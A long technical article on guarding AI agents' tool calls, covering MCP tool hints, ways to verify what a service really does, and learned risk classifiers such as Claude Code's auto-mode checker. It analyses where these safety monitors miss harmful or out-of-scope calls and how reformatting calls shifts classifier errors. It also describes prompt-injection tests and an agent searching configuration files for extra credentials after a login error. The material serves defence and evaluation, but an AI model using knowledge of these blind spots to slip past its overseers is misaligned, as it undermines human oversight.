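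New labels also create work, because every developer must learn them and every host needs a rule for handling them. Jonathan Hefner, who helps maintain MCP, objected to an early version of the governance proposal because it wasn't clear how its annotations would change a client's behaviour. The blog post uses this objection as a test for new proposals. A developer can meanwhile try a private label in a tool's `_meta` field, but a general-purpose host won't recognise it.

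### What suppliers actually declare

Trofimov and Novikov measured how often MCP servers use the four hints. They started with all 18,688 distinct servers in the official MCP registry on 27 July 2026 and left out 9,454 that had no address for remote use. They asked each of the other 9,234 for its list of tools, and 4,838 returned at least one, for a total of 98,291 tools. They read the hints without calling any tool.

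Of the 98,291 tools, 74.0% have at least one hint set and 61.7% have all four. Much of this labelling comes from one publisher, named in the registry as `io.github.pipeworx-io`, which supplied 45.0% of the tools and set all four hints on every one.

| Share of tools | All tools | Without the largest publisher |
|---|---|---|
| At least one hint | 74.0% | 52.8% |
| All four hints | 61.7% | 30.3% |
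| No hints | 26.0% | 47.2% |
| Read-only, non-destructive, idempotent and open-world | 39.9% | 7.3% |
| `destructiveHint` set on a tool that is not read-only | 12.9% | 11.7% |
| Labelled as destructive, and not read-only | 3.1% | 3.2% |

The figures that exclude the largest publisher better indicate what a guard will find on an unfamiliar server, because they reflect the choices of many developers. Nearly half of the remaining tools have no hints, so the guard has to assume the worst about them.

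`destructiveHint` appears on 65.8% of all tools, but most of these are also marked read-only, which makes the hint irrelevant. The hint applies to only 12.9% of all tools; 3.1% are marked as destructive, which leaves about 9.8% marked as making only additive changes. The hint can spare the user a question only for this last group, because a guard already treats an unlabelled tool as destructive.

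The census counts tools rather than calls, so a rarely used tool counts as much as a popular one. It also leaves out servers that run only on the user's own computer and more than 4,000 remote servers that didn't respond. If a guard's users install tools only from the Anthropic and OpenAI directories, labels will probably be more common than in the census.

### What the hints cannot express

Suppose an agent pays an invoice and the connection fails before the response arrives. When the agent proposes its next call, the guard has to judge it without knowing whether the payment went through. Trofimov and Novikov describe three mistakes the agent could make. If it sends the payment again, it may pay twice. If it assumes the payment succeeded and finishes the task, the invoice may remain unpaid. If it requests a refund to be safe, it may receive money for a payment that never happened.

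The guard could judge these calls better if it knew three things about the service, none of which the hints can fully express:

| Missing information | How it would help | Nearest hint |
|---|---|---|
| Idempotency key: which argument holds it | The guard can allow a retry with the same key | `idempotentHint`, which names no argument |
| Outcome query: which call reports whether the payment happened | The agent can check before it pays again | None |
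| Compensation: which call undoes the payment, and under what conditions | The guard can stop a refund until the agent has confirmed the payment | None |

The idempotency hint has no correct value for some tools. If a payment tool accepts an optional idempotency key, repeating a call is safe only with the key, but the developer has to choose true or false for the whole tool. Smithy avoids this problem because its label marks the field that holds the key.

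The hints also cannot describe a provisional call, such as a hotel reservation that expires unless the agent confirms it. If the hints declared the expiry, a guard could allow the reservation and ask the user only about the confirmation. The hints also cannot express which pairs of calls commute, because each hint belongs to a single tool.

In November 2025, MCP added a partial form of outcome query through an experimental feature called tasks. The server returns an identifier for a long-running call, which the host can use to check whether the call has finished. But if the connection fails before the identifier arrives, the host still can't tell whether the call went through. Cancelling a task requests that the server stop, but does not undo what it has already done.

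A vendor can still offer an idempotency key, a status call and a conditional refund through ordinary tools, and explain them in the tools' descriptions. But every vendor will do this differently, so whoever writes a guard has to study each service to use them.

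## Checking what a service really does

A guard's owner does not have to accept an unverified declaration. Trofimov and Novikov note that only an analysis of the implementations could measure the gap between what tools declare and what they do. An owner can check part of what a single service does, using whatever the supplier makes available: source code, documentation, a test account, a dry run (asking the service to report what a call would do without doing it) or queries about the call's target.

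### Comparing descriptions with source code

Many MCP servers are open source, so the owner can compare what a tool's description promises with what its code does. Shi, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Description-Code Inconsistency in Real-world MCP Servers*, automated this comparison in June with a program called DCIChecker. It works in three steps:

1. It finds each tool in the server's code and extracts the name, the argument list and the description, which are all that the agent's model sees.
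2. It collects the tool's main function, the project's own functions that it calls, up to three levels deep, and any sensitive operations such as network requests.
3. It asks a language model whether the description and the code are consistent, then asks separately whether they are inconsistent. If the two answers differ, a third prompt weighs the explanations and decides.

The wording of the question strongly affected the results. On a hand-labelled sample, the model found only 47% of the mismatches when the researchers asked whether the description and code agreed. When they asked whether the two disagreed, it found all of them, but about a fifth of the mismatches it reported were false. An owner who asks a model to review a tool should therefore ask both questions.

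The researchers ran DCIChecker on 19,200 tools from 2,214 Python servers. It could not check 2,170 of the tools because they had no description. It flagged 1,907 of the other 17,030, which is 11.2% of the tools it could check and 9.9% of the whole sample. About 35% of the servers had at least one flagged tool.

| Kind of mismatch | Example from a published server |
|---|---|
| Overclaimed function | A trading tool promises to ask for the user's approval but submits the order at once |
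| Undeclared function | A tool that should repeat a message also returns a secret key |
| Wrong function | A weather tool looks up exchange rates |
| Ambiguous description | "Process some data" |
| Undeclared change | A tool that saves code to a file also changes the file's permissions |
| Undeclared use of resources | A tool that returns a document's text also leaves files on the disk |
| Undeclared disclosure | A "local" PDF converter uploads the document to an outside service |

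The first four kinds made up 75.2% of the mismatches, and overclaiming alone made up 35.4%. Many of these only waste the agent's time, as the weather tool does, so not all of the 11.2% of tools with mismatches are dangerous. The last three kinds made up 24.8% of the mismatches, or about 2.8% of the tools checked. That figure is a little too low for a guard's purposes, because the researchers counted each tool under one main kind, and some overclaiming tools, such as the trading tool, also have undeclared effects.

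To measure accuracy, the researchers checked 200 flagged and 200 unflagged tools by hand. Eight of the flagged tools were false alarms, and five of the unflagged ones had a mismatch that DCIChecker had missed. DCIChecker therefore caught 192 of the 197 real mismatches in the sample, which is the published recall of 97.5%. But half of the sample was flagged tools, while in the full set unflagged tools outnumber flagged ones by about eight to one. If 2.5% of all 15,123 unflagged tools have a mismatch, DCIChecker missed about 380, and its recall across the full set is closer to 83%. Because that estimate rests on five errors, anything from about 68% to 94% is plausible.

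Mismatches also cluster in a few servers. The 8.3% of servers with three or more mismatches accounted for 60% of the total. An owner who finds one false description should read the rest of that server's code before trusting the server.

### Deriving a tool's effects and enforcing them

Once the owner knows what a tool's code can do, software can restrict the tool to those actions. *Towards Practically-Secure Tools for AI Agents* (Adam, Lu and colleagues, 2026), a proposal from Brown University, combines static analysis with a sandbox. Static analysis examines code without running it and lists every effect the code could have. A sandbox checks operations while the program runs and stops any that break a rule.

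Their example is a tool that writes text to a file. To imitate a real leak, they added code that reports the tool's use to an outside server, and left the description unchanged. The analysis produces a summary that includes these lines:

```
input(path)    -> effect(fs:write)
input(content) -> effect(net:write)
```

The second line reveals the hidden report, because it shows that the text the user wants to save affects what the tool sends over the network. The first line is less useful. The agent chooses the path when it calls the tool, so the analysis can't rule out the tool overwriting any file. A guard that relied on the analysis alone would have to reject the tool whenever the user wanted to restrict writing to one folder.

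The tool's developer solves this problem by wrapping each file or network operation in a small sandbox that accepts new rules with every call. The analyser then confirms that every such operation is inside a sandbox and that the tool's code cannot change the rules. When the agent proposes a call, the guard compares the summary with the user's policy, then either blocks the call or sends it on with rules such as "write only inside the workspace folder".

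Adam and colleagues tested a prototype on one MCP server written in Rust. They replayed three recorded sessions, each in an acceptable version and a harmful one. In one session, the agent published a project on GitHub, and in the harmful version a settings file contained a secret key.

| Protection | Acceptable versions allowed | Harmful versions blocked |
|---|---|---|
| None | 3 of 3 | 0 of 3 |
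| One fixed sandbox around the server | 2 of 3 | 1 of 3 |
| Code analysis alone | 2 of 3 | 3 of 3 |
| Analysis and a sandbox for each operation | 3 of 3 | 3 of 3 |

Six cases that the designers picked show that the idea can work, but they can't be used to estimate a miss rate. The designers also assumed that someone had already written the right policy for each call. In real use, tool developers would have to change their code, and a remote server would have to prove that it runs the program the analyser examined. Adam and colleagues expect more needless refusals with Python and JavaScript, which are harder to analyse than Rust.

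*AgentBound* (Bühler, Biagiola and colleagues, 2025) requires less work from developers. A language model reads a server's source code and drafts a list of the permissions it needs, such as reading files, deleting files or contacting the network. A container, which isolates a program from the rest of the computer, then enforces the list without any change to the server. The researchers drafted lists for 296 popular servers and asked the developers of 96 to check them. Of the lists whose developers replied, 80.9% were correct as drafted. The container can stop a maps tool from contacting an undeclared address, but it can't stop a tool from misusing a permission it legitimately has. For example, a mail tool needs access to the mail provider, so the container can't stop it from sending the wrong email.

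### Where local code stops

A local tool's code shows which request the tool sends, but not what the remote service does with it. For example, the code of the community-made `volume_delete` tool contains neither the cascade that hid PocketOS's backups nor the later 48-hour delay, because both are in Railway's own code.

Adam and colleagues acknowledge this limit and say it also applies to databases and shell commands. Their prototype restricts network access by domain, so it can't distinguish reading a post on a social network from publishing one.

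If the code is hard to follow, the owner can run the tool and record what it sends. The sandbox in *Evaluating Privilege Usage of Agents with Real-World Tools* (2026) runs real MCP servers, including ones for email and the note-taking service Notion, and logs their requests to outside services. Such a log would show which remote operation a vaguely named tool uses but, like the code, would not show what the outside service does with the request. *Exposed by Design* (2026) points out that static analysis of source code also cannot reveal a deployment's settings or the access checks that a running server applies.

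### Working from the documentation alone

Some services publish no code. Zhang, Hu and colleagues (2026) found in *No-Box Vulnerability Analysis* that 3,007 of the 18,770 active servers in the official MCP registry (16.0%) offered a remote address but neither a released package nor a link to source code. Their September study tested how much a program can predict from tool descriptions alone.

The program, MCPSEC, checks for one risk, that a tool passes text written by an attacker to the agent's model, which may then follow instructions in it. This risk depends on what a tool returns, so the results are only indirect evidence about predicting what a call changes or spends. MCPSEC prompts a language model to guess how each tool works and where its data comes from. It then rates the risk on four scales: how faithfully the tool preserves outside text, how easily an attacker could plant that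 text, whether the output can carry instructions, and whether the tool filters it. It also writes an attack scenario for each tool it considers vulnerable.

Zhang and colleagues applied MCPSEC to 177 tools from 20 popular open-source servers, and it flagged 143. Team members rated the flagged tools twice, first from the descriptions and then with access to the source code.

| Measure | Descriptions only | With source code |
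|---|---|---|
| Agreement with the raters on risk levels | 83.6% (four scales) | 66.4% (three scales) |
| Attack scenarios rated plausible | 85.3% | 73.4% |

Raters did not rejudge how easily an attacker could plant the text, because source code adds nothing about that, so the two agreement figures cover different scales. On the three scales they judged twice, agreement with MCPSEC fell from 82.5% to 66.4%. MCPSEC's answers did not change, so the whole drop came from raters changing theirs. The first figure mostly measured whether people and a model make the same guesses from the same description.

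The guesses were least accurate about what a tool returns. Many tools that seemed to pass on outside text actually returned only an identifier, a count or a status code. Most errors overstated the risk, and MCPSEC flagged 94 of the 95 tools that the researchers later confirmed as vulnerable. However, it also flagged 81% of all the tools, and the researchers could not establish that any of the unconfirmed tools were safe, so its false-alarm rate is unknown.

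This kind of prediction costs an average of $1.65 per server, which makes it a cheap way to decide what to examine first. Like an untrusted hint, it can justify raising a risk class but not lowering one.

### Trying calls in a test account

With a test account, the owner can make a call and see what happens. Bellibatlu, Wang and Zhang (2026), in *Do Agent Benchmarks Do What They Say?*, developed a systematic way to do this with the simulated tools in agent benchmarks. They turned each tool's documentation into conditions that a program can check. The program then recorded the simulator's state before and after a call and compared the two.

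The documentation for a simulated telephone company's `refuel_data` tool required an active line, but when the program tried a suspended line, the tool added 40 gigabytes of data and an $80 bill. In a medical benchmark, researchers found that the agent receives a message confirming each change to a patient's record, although the simulator never changes any record. A guard's owner should therefore compare the state before and after a test call instead of relying on the response.

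Even with full access to the simulators, the researchers' checker missed most of the defects they planted. In 29 of the 33 misses they scored, one of the conditions covered the defect, but no test call had triggered it. On τ²-bench, the checker could not grade 96 of 180 conditions because no test call reached the state they described. An owner will usually see less of a live service than these researchers saw of their simulators, and may be unable to reset it between tests.

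A useful test on a live service needs invented data, a second user and an email address outside the organisation. The owner lists everything in the account, makes the call and lists everything again. The owner then checks for messages at the outside address, new charges on the bill and changes in who has access. Finally, the owner tries to undo the call with the same credential the agent will use, since an undo that only works in the supplier's dashboard doesn't help the agent. On Railway in April 2026, running this test on a spare volume with a backup would have shown that the call destroyed the backup and had no undo.

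A test account can still be misleading because little depends on it. For example, an edit to an empty GitHub project triggers none of the workflows that the same edit could start in the company's main project.

### Previewing a call with a dry run

A dry run covers the real target, which a test account cannot do. Azure, Microsoft's cloud service, has a detailed one called what-if. Customers describe the resources they want in a file, and what-if compares the file with what already exists. An example in Microsoft's *Bicep What-If* starts with a virtual network that has two subnets, which are sections of the network. The new file leaves one of them out. The following command and output are adapted and much shortened:

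```
az deployment group what-if -g Shop --template-file network.bicep

  ~ vnet-001
    ~ properties.subnets: [
      - 0: name: "subnet001"
Resource changes: 1 to modify.
```

The minus sign marks the subnet that the change would delete. The agent would make the change by running `az deployment group create`, and a guard that judged the command by its name would not expect a deletion. The guard also has to read the whole preview, because Azure treats a subnet as a property of its network and so the last line shows one modification and no deletions.

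The preview leaves out several things:

| What is missing | What the guard sees |
|---|---|
| Resources that the file brings in through a template link | Nothing |
| Modules that depend on values Azure can't work out in advance | A warning in recent versions of the command-line program, nothing in older ones |
| Resources beyond 500 nested templates, 800 resource groups or five minutes of processing | "Ignore" |
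| Resource types that what-if doesn't cover | "Unsupported", according to Microsoft's *Deployments* |

"Ignore" is the most misleading entry, because Azure uses it both for resources that the deployment will leave alone and for resources that what-if did not check after reaching a limit. A guard should treat it as unknown if the deployment is large enough to reach a limit. What-if also reports some changes that won't happen, such as the removal of values that Azure fills in automatically, so a guard that stopped every predicted deletion would block some deployments by mistake. The preview covers only configuration. The example output doesn't show what the change would cost or which programs were using the deleted subnet.

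By default, what-if requires the same write permissions as the deployment, so a credential that can preview a change can usually also make it. Customers can choose a setting that checks only for permission to read each resource.

Other suppliers use "dry run" for something much more limited. In AWS's server rental service (EC2), the `DryRun` parameter only checks whether the caller has permission and does not predict any effects. In its encryption key service (KMS), a dry run checks the permission and the parameters, but AWS charges for it as an ordinary request and counts it towards the customer's quota. The owner should find out what a dry run does, preferably in a test account, before letting a guard use it automatically.

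### Looking up the target

A guard can also make its own calls before it decides. For example, looking up volume `3d2c42fb-...` could have shown that it belonged to PocketOS's production environment.

Lin and Milani Fard (2025) designed an evaluator around this idea in *A Context-Aware LLM-Based Action Safety Evaluator for Automation Agents*. It runs an agent's planned actions in order as long as they only read information, such as listing the programs running on a computer. At the first action that might change something, it stops and has a language model simulate the results of that action and the rest. It then uses one prompt to describe the risks and another to judge whether the plan is safe.

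Lin and Milani Fard tested the final judgement on R-Judge, a benchmark of 162 agent cases. With GPT-3.5 as the judge, accuracy was 54.9% without a description of the risks, 73.5% with one written by GPT-4 and 75.3% with one written by people. With GPT-4 as the judge and the human descriptions, it was 78.4%. These figures are good evidence that a written description of the risks helped those models, which are now old. Whether looking things up also helps is still untested, because the part of the system they tested could not yet use the facts gathered by the read-only calls. They list that comparison as future work.

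The design is also circular, because the guard must already be able to identify read-only calls to gather facts safely, and identifying them is often the purpose of the check. Lin and Milani Fard assume that GET requests are safe and ask a language model to pick out the read-only actions. If the model used the same assumption to classify Telegram's `GET .../sendMessage` as read-only, the evaluator would send the message while checking whether sending it was safe.

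The guard can avoid this circularity if the owner gives it a short, fixed list of lookups that other evidence has already shown to be read-only. For a hosting company, two lookups might be enough, one that returns a volume's environment and one that lists its backups. The guard should choose the lookup itself and keep the result away from the agent, in case the result contains a secret.

### Admitting a new service

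An owner can combine these methods into a procedure for each new service, using the Reversibility Classes from R0 (no effect) to R4 (irreversible):

1. List every operation the agent could call, and put each one in R4 as unknown.
2. Read the source code of any local tool, or log its requests, and note which remote operations it uses and what else it does.
3. Read the documentation and any declared hints. Use them to plan the tests and to spot operations that should stay in R4.
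4. Try the remaining operations in a test account, starting with those that appear only to read. Vary the arguments, and attempt an undo after each change.
5. Find out whether the service offers a dry run, and what that dry run leaves out.
6. Record the class of each operation with its conditions, the evidence, the date and an expiry date. For a local tool, add the version and a hash of its code.

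One observed harm is enough to keep an operation in a high-risk class. Moving it to a lower-risk class requires more evidence, because a test that finds no harm may have used arguments that don't trigger it.

| Evidence | Class it supports |
|---|---|
| A harmless description, name or hint | None; the operation stays unknown |
| Complete source code of a local tool that contacts no other program or service | The class that fits the effects in the code, for that version only |
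| Source code of a tool that calls a remote service | None until the owner has tested the remote operation |
| Documentation describes a read, and varied test calls change nothing, send nothing outside and return nothing secret | R0, for the kinds of arguments tested |
| The agent's own credential restores the exact earlier state, and nobody outside saw the change | R1, as long as nobody else changes the target first |
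| A further call reaches an acceptable result at a known, limited cost | R2 |
| Recovery needs a person or the supplier | R3 |
| A message reaches the outside address, or nobody can restore the data | R4, now confirmed |
| A complete dry run with no ignored or unsupported entries | A class for that one call, if the dry run covers the relevant kinds of effect |

The risk class of Railway's `volumeDelete` now depends on whether the agent's token can cancel a deletion during the 48-hour delay. If it can, and both the data and the backups return intact, the owner can put the call in R1 on condition that the agent can still cancel in time. If only a person using the dashboard can cancel the deletion, the call belongs in R3, and the guard should ask each time.

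## Using a learned risk classifier

Testing an operation properly takes time, and an agent may call one that nobody has tested. A learned risk classifier can rate any call, even one to a service its developers had never heard of, but it is hard to know which ratings to trust.

### Inputs and outputs

A classifier usually receives more than the call itself. TS-Guard, a trained model described in *ToolSafe* (2026), takes the user's request, the agent's earlier steps, the descriptions of the available tools and the call the agent plans to make. It returns a safety rating for that call. With invented values, an exchange might look like this:

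```
request:  Remove my old test volumes
history:  list_volumes() -> 3d2c42fb-..., 91aa07e4-...
tools:    volume_delete: deletes a volume
call:     volume_delete(volumeId="3d2c42fb-...")

rating:   0.5 (possibly unsafe)
```

Other classifiers return a yes or no, a probability for each of several rules, or a verdict with written reasons. The guard's author decides whether each result means allowing the call, asking about it or blocking it. If the classifier returns a probability of harm, blocking at a lower probability lets fewer harmful calls through but blocks more harmless ones.

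### Small trained classifiers and prompted language models

Developers train a small text classifier on labelled examples. It can run on the user's own computer at little cost, but it learns only the distinction in those examples. A prompted language model is a general-purpose model that receives written instructions with each call. Developers can change its rules by editing the instructions, and its training data probably included a lot about common commands and services, but it usually costs more per call.

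A classifier trained on examples that don't fit its job can block ordinary actions, as a test in *PARALLAX* (Fokou, 2026) shows. Fokou's guard, Parallax, includes DeBERTa, a small language model trained on about 16,000 texts to recognise prompt injection, which is text containing instructions meant to take over an AI system. The model classified 98.8% of the held-out texts correctly. But when Fokou gave the guard 50 ordinary agent actions, such as writing files, running builds and sending email, it blocked 18 of them (36%), and DeBERTa caused 14 of those blocks.

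DeBERTa had learned to distinguish injected text from harmless text, not harmful actions from harmless ones. It can therefore flag a routine action because of the contents of a file or an email. Its confidence was 1.00 in all 14 cases, so a stricter threshold would not have helped.

Fokou's default settings therefore skip DeBERTa for seven kinds of action, including HTTP requests, emails and file deletions, and send them to a prompted language model instead. With these settings, the guard blocked 277 of 280 attacks, down from all 280, and none of the 50 ordinary actions. Fokou had added rules after earlier tests exposed gaps, so these figures come from a guard adjusted to its test. Because the test included only 50 ordinary actions, the true rate of wrongly blocked actions could still plausibly be up to about 7%. The trained classifier also no longer classifies many of the calls that matter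 most to a guard for outside services.

Llama Guard 3, which Meta trained to recognise harmful content in conversations, had a similar problem. *What Can Be Enforced?* (2026) used it to judge agents' actions. It missed 15% of a curated set of violations and 46% of the injected actions from AgentDojo, with false-block rates of 9% and 10% respectively.

Some small classifiers are also sensitive to how an agent writes a call. Demirkiran and Ernstberger (2026), in *ToolRosetta*, rewrote the same actions in several forms, such as these:

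```
{"tool": "reserve_hotel", "hotel": "Riverside"}
reserve_hotel(hotel="Riverside")
reserve-hotel --hotel Riverside
```

Changing AgentDojo's calls from the first form, JSON, to the shell command in the last line raised the false-block rates of four of five specialised classifiers by 21 to 47 percentage points. TS-Guard's rose from 7.8% to 29%. The error rates of the two leading commercial models in the test changed by at most 3.4 points. One specialised model, StepGuard, was also stable, so small size alone doesn't explain the problem. A parser that restored these rewritten calls to their original form removed the effect completely, which is another reason to parse a call before judging it.

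### Well-known and unfamiliar services

A language model can often tell what a popular payment service's refund request does without a rule for it, because documentation, forum answers and sample programs in its training data describe the operation many times. A company's private service may not appear in that data. If an agent sends `POST /v2/ledger/settle` to such a service, the model can only infer the effect from the ordinary meanings of "ledger" and "settle". The request might mark an invoice as paid or actually pay it, and the model may sound equally confident about either.

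Research on related tasks supports this explanation. In *On Mitigating Code LLM Hallucinations with API Documentation* (2024), every model tested made many errors when writing calls to rarely seen cloud APIs, even if it did well on common ones. *PhantomBench* (2026) describes the same pattern for facts in general, with models more likely to invent information about concepts that are rarer in the training data. Neither tested whether models can judge a call's risk, and the 2024 models are now old.

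No 2026 test appears to compare a classifier's errors on well-known services with its errors on unknown ones. The closest is *Decision Models as Policy Gates for Coding Agents*, which tested 24 models on 2,643 synthetic tool calls, including some to 53 real MCP servers. The models had to match each call against written rules such as "permanently deletes data". In one version of the test, the rules' examples described operations in general terms instead of naming commands, tools and services. The ten strongest models detected almost as many hazards as they did with the named examples, while the detection rates of six weaker models fell by 2 to 10 percentage points.

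The strong models evidently recognised what a command did without needing a rule that named it. But the calls kept their real names, so the test does not show how the models would handle a name they had never encountered. Kovalenko and Redchych found a related weakness in small agents. The agents learned to ask before making destructive calls, but they associated the habit with particular tool names and lost much of it with unfamiliar tools.

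A good tool description reduces the need for prior knowledge of the service. In *When Neither Side Confirms* (2026), a language model labeled MCP tools as destructive or not, and its labels matched the reviewers' consensus for 51 of the 56 tools the reviewers were sure about. In the other five cases, the model called a reversible or harmless action destructive.

A tool's description doesn't specify what an organisation permits. Karunanithi (2026), in *Per-Attack Blocking Hides Catalog Vulnerability*, gave models the names and descriptions of 28 tools and asked what role each tool played and where its output could go. Three leading models got the role right in 82 of 84 answers, but for sensitive data they allowed at least one forbidden destination in 27 of 57 answers. When Karunanithi added the organisation's rule to the prompt, that number fell to zero.

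Training data can also go out of date, so a model may not know about Railway's 48-hour delay.

### How Claude Code's classifier works

Claude Code's auto mode uses a prompted language model to approve or block calls. According to the *Claude Code Complete User Handbook* (2026), terminal and VS Code sessions have started in this mode by default on every plan since version 2.1.283. Anthropic described the design and its first results in March 2026.

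Calls that match an allow rule skip the classifier. Edits to files inside the project also skip it, because the user can review them through version control. The classifier judges all other calls, including shell commands, web requests and calls to outside tools.

Anthropic's classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. Anthropic removes the agent's explanations of its actions so that a persuasive justification can't influence the decision. It also removes the results of tool calls, since a web page or file may contain planted instructions. Without those results, if the agent tries to cancel job `abc123`, the classifier can't tell whether the agent found that identifier in a list or made it up.

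Anthropic tried other combinations of inputs. Including the agent's text and the tool results made the classifier worse at catching actions that went beyond the user's request. Using only the tool calls produced the fewest misses, but the classifier blocked things users had plainly asked for.

The decision takes one or two stages:

1. A fast filter gives a single yes-or-no answer, with instructions to block if in doubt. If it doesn't flag the call, the call runs.
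2. If the filter flags the call, the model reads the same input again and reasons step by step before deciding.

The instructions contain more than twenty block rules covering destroying or leaking data, weakening security, acting on things the agent has no reason to trust, and bypassing review or interfering with other people's work. A short list of exceptions permits routine actions, such as installing packages that the project already lists. The model checks the block rules, then the exceptions, then whether the user authorised the action.

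The instructions also define a trust boundary around the user's environment. By default, it includes only the code repository where the agent is working, but users can add their own storage, code-hosting organisation and internal services. The classifier treats sending data anywhere else as a possible leak.

Some of these rules work even if the model has no information about the service. An unfamiliar host is outside the trust boundary whatever its operations do. Another rule covers searching for usable credentials. In one of Anthropic's examples, which resembles the PocketOS case, an agent hit a login error and then looked through configuration files for other tokens. A classifier that stopped an agent at that point would not need to work out what `volumeDelete` does.

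### The March 2026 results

Anthropic tested the classifier on three sets of actions:

| | Ordinary calls blocked (10,000 real calls) | Overeager actions missed (52 real actions) | Data leaks missed (1,000 synthetic attempts) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Fast filter alone | 8.5% | 6.6% | 1.8% |
| Both stages | 0.4% | 17% | 5.7% |

The reasoning stage examines only calls that the filter has flagged and either confirms the block or releases the call, so it can add misses but not reduce them. It released about 95% of the acceptable calls that the filter had flagged, but also about 11% of the overeager ones, in which the agent tries to help but goes beyond what the user authorised.

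Suppose an agent makes 10,000 calls, ten of which the guard should stop. At these rates, the filter alone would block about 850 acceptable calls and miss fewer than one dangerous call on average. With both stages, the guard would block about 40 acceptable calls and miss one or two dangerous ones. That may be an acceptable trade-off for everyday coding, but it may not be if one missed call could delete a company's database. The two-stage miss rate is also uncertain because it comes from only 52 actions, and the true figure could plausibly be from 9% to 30%.

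In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier had identified the danger. For example, it identified a force-push, which can overwrite other people's work in a shared code repository. But it treated the user's request to "clean up the PR" (a proposed code change) as permission, although the user had not mentioned force-pushing. In other cases, it treated approval of one action as approval of a similar one.

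Deciding whether someone has consented is harder than recognising a deletion, because people phrase requests loosely and expect the agent to fill in the details. Anthropic tried to correct these errors by changing the instructions but found no version that helped more than it hurt. It says auto mode is much safer than running an agent with no checks, but should not replace careful human review for high-stakes infrastructure.

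### Testing three permission checkers

Yang, Zhou and colleagues (November 2026) examined consent more closely in *Explicit Authorization Scope Improves LLM-Based Permission Checking in Coding Agents*. They tested the classifiers, or "permission checkers", in Claude Code, OpenAI's Codex and Alibaba's Qwen Code.

Each agent attempted 128 development and operations tasks, which involved cancelling jobs, restarting services, and deleting code branches and old files. It also attempted 244 banking and chat cases from AgentDojo that contained planted instructions. This gave 1,116 runs across the three products. The AgentDojo cases yielded only false-block rates, so all the evidence about misses comes from the development and operations tasks.

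For each operations task, an answer key lists the objects the agent may change. The researchers labelled a call authorised if every object it named was on that list, and out of scope otherwise. In one task, a user asked the agent to delete old experiment files for a range of tickets. The answer key permitted deleting only the user's own files, but the request didn't mention this limit. The agent proposed deleting a colleague's files, and the checker approved the call.

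Claude Code's checker approved 13 of 24 out-of-scope calls (54%) and blocked 37% of authorised calls. Qwen Code's approved 28 of 35 out-of-scope calls (80%) and blocked 31% of authorised ones, while Codex's approved 78 of 84 (93%) and blocked 10%. The Codex and Qwen Code checkers blocked a larger share of authorised calls than of out-of-scope ones, although the differences could be due to chance.

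Stronger models did not solve the problem. The researchers sent the recorded calls to a more capable model from each vendor, without carrying them out. Codex's misses rose from 77 to 82 out of 84, and Qwen Code's from 25 to 26 out of 35. Claude Code's fell from 10 to 1 out of 24, but only because the stronger model refused all the second-stage questions and Claude Code treats a refusal as a block. False blocks on 224 authorised calls in the AgentDojo cases rose from 23 to 134.

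More information about the targets did not help much either. In a separate test, nine models judged 227 of the recorded calls using the same procedure. Their combined miss rate was 58% with the usual input, 62% when they also received the results of earlier tool calls, and 59% when the researchers added each target's current owner and status. But false blocks fell from 25% to 16%.

The reason is that 132 of the 143 out-of-scope calls broke rules that appeared in neither the user's request nor the results of earlier tool calls. Learning that a file belongs to a colleague doesn't help if nobody has said that colleagues' files are off limits. The researchers therefore added a sentence to each request stating its scope, for example that the agent may delete only files in the `dev` environment that belong to `alex` and to the `auth` component. They then had each product's checker judge the same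 calls again:

| Checker | Misses, original request | Misses, scope stated | False blocks, original request | False blocks, scope stated |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | 67% | 8% | 42% | 2% |
| Codex | 92% | 20–26% | 10% | 3% |
| Qwen Code | 80% | 20% | 29% | 2% |

The original-request figures differ slightly from the earlier ones because the checkers' answers can vary between runs. The range for Codex covers two runs.

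Stating the scope also made information about the targets useful. Under the common procedure, the combined miss rate fell from 58% to 9% with the scope stated, to 2% when the models also received earlier tool results, and to 1% with the targets' current details. For example, a command to cancel a job contains only the job's identifier, so a checker given the rule that the agent may cancel only `alex`'s jobs still needs the job's owner. Neither Claude Code's checker nor Qwen Code's reads the earlier results that would show the owner.

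Some of Codex's remaining errors had a different cause. Its checker rates both the risk of a call and how clearly the user authorised it. In one run with the scope stated, it gave 30 out-of-scope calls a low authorisation rating and a medium risk rating, then approved 16 of them. For 15 of the 16, its written reasons included that the change was reversible, limited or small. A guard's author can prevent this by requiring clear authorisation at every risk rating.

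The agents also behaved better when they received the scope themselves. In 384 new runs of the operations tasks, no agent proposed an out-of-scope call. The share of tasks that ended in the correct state rose from 25% to 94% for Claude Code, from 34% to 99% for Codex and from 21% to 49% for Qwen Code.

These are best-case results, because the researchers took the scope statements from the answer key. Real users would have to think of the limits themselves and might leave some out. The study did not test incomplete or mistaken statements.

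### Why the miss rates differ

Anthropic reported a 17% miss rate for Claude Code, while Yang and colleagues measured 54%. Their later test used a newer checker model, so the higher rate isn't due to an older model. The two samples are very different.

Anthropic took its 52 actions from employees' real sessions, where an employee had refused each action or someone had flagged it afterwards. The sample therefore leaves out overeager actions that nobody noticed. The operations benchmark deliberately leaves the limits of a request unclear, and its labels depend on an answer key that the checker never receives. A careful person with only the checker's information would probably have approved many of the same calls. The 54% is therefore a better guide to vague requests on shared systems than to coding in general.

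The gap in false blocks is even wider, at 0.4% in Anthropic's test and 37% on the operations tasks. Anthropic used 10,000 everyday tool calls, many of them probably routine. The 52 authorised calls in the operations test came from tasks about deleting, cancelling and restarting things, which a cautious checker can reasonably flag. Anthropic doesn't say whether its 10,000 calls include those that allow rules would have cleared anyway. If they do, the false-block rate among calls that reach the classifier is higher than 0.4%.

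Neither sample was meant to represent calls to unfamiliar third-party services. A company that wants a figure for its own agents would have to label some of those agents' calls.

### Writing clearer rules

The guard's own rules can be as vague as a user's request. For example, it is unclear whether "permanently deletes data" covers moving a file to the trash or doing a dry run of a deletion. *Decision Models as Policy Gates for Coding Agents* measured how much it helps to add examples and counterexamples to such rules.

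Most of the models tested were decision models, a type introduced in September 2026 that returns a probability for each question without generating text. With one-sentence rules, a decision model called Jev 1.14 detected 89.3% of the hazards but interrupted 77 of 252 harmless actions (30.6%). With examples and counterexamples, it detected 98.2% of the hazards and interrupted 12 harmless actions (4.8%). It typically answered in 120 milliseconds and cost $0.46 per thousand requests.

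The many interruptions came from small errors that added up. Jev checked every action against 23 rules and wrongly matched a rule 2.49% of the time. If those errors were independent, the chance of at least one on a harmless action would be

```
1 − (1 − 0.0249)^23 ≈ 44%
```

The actual rate was lower, which suggests the errors tended to fall on the same actions. But even a rule with few false alarms can noticeably raise the total when a guard applies it to every call.

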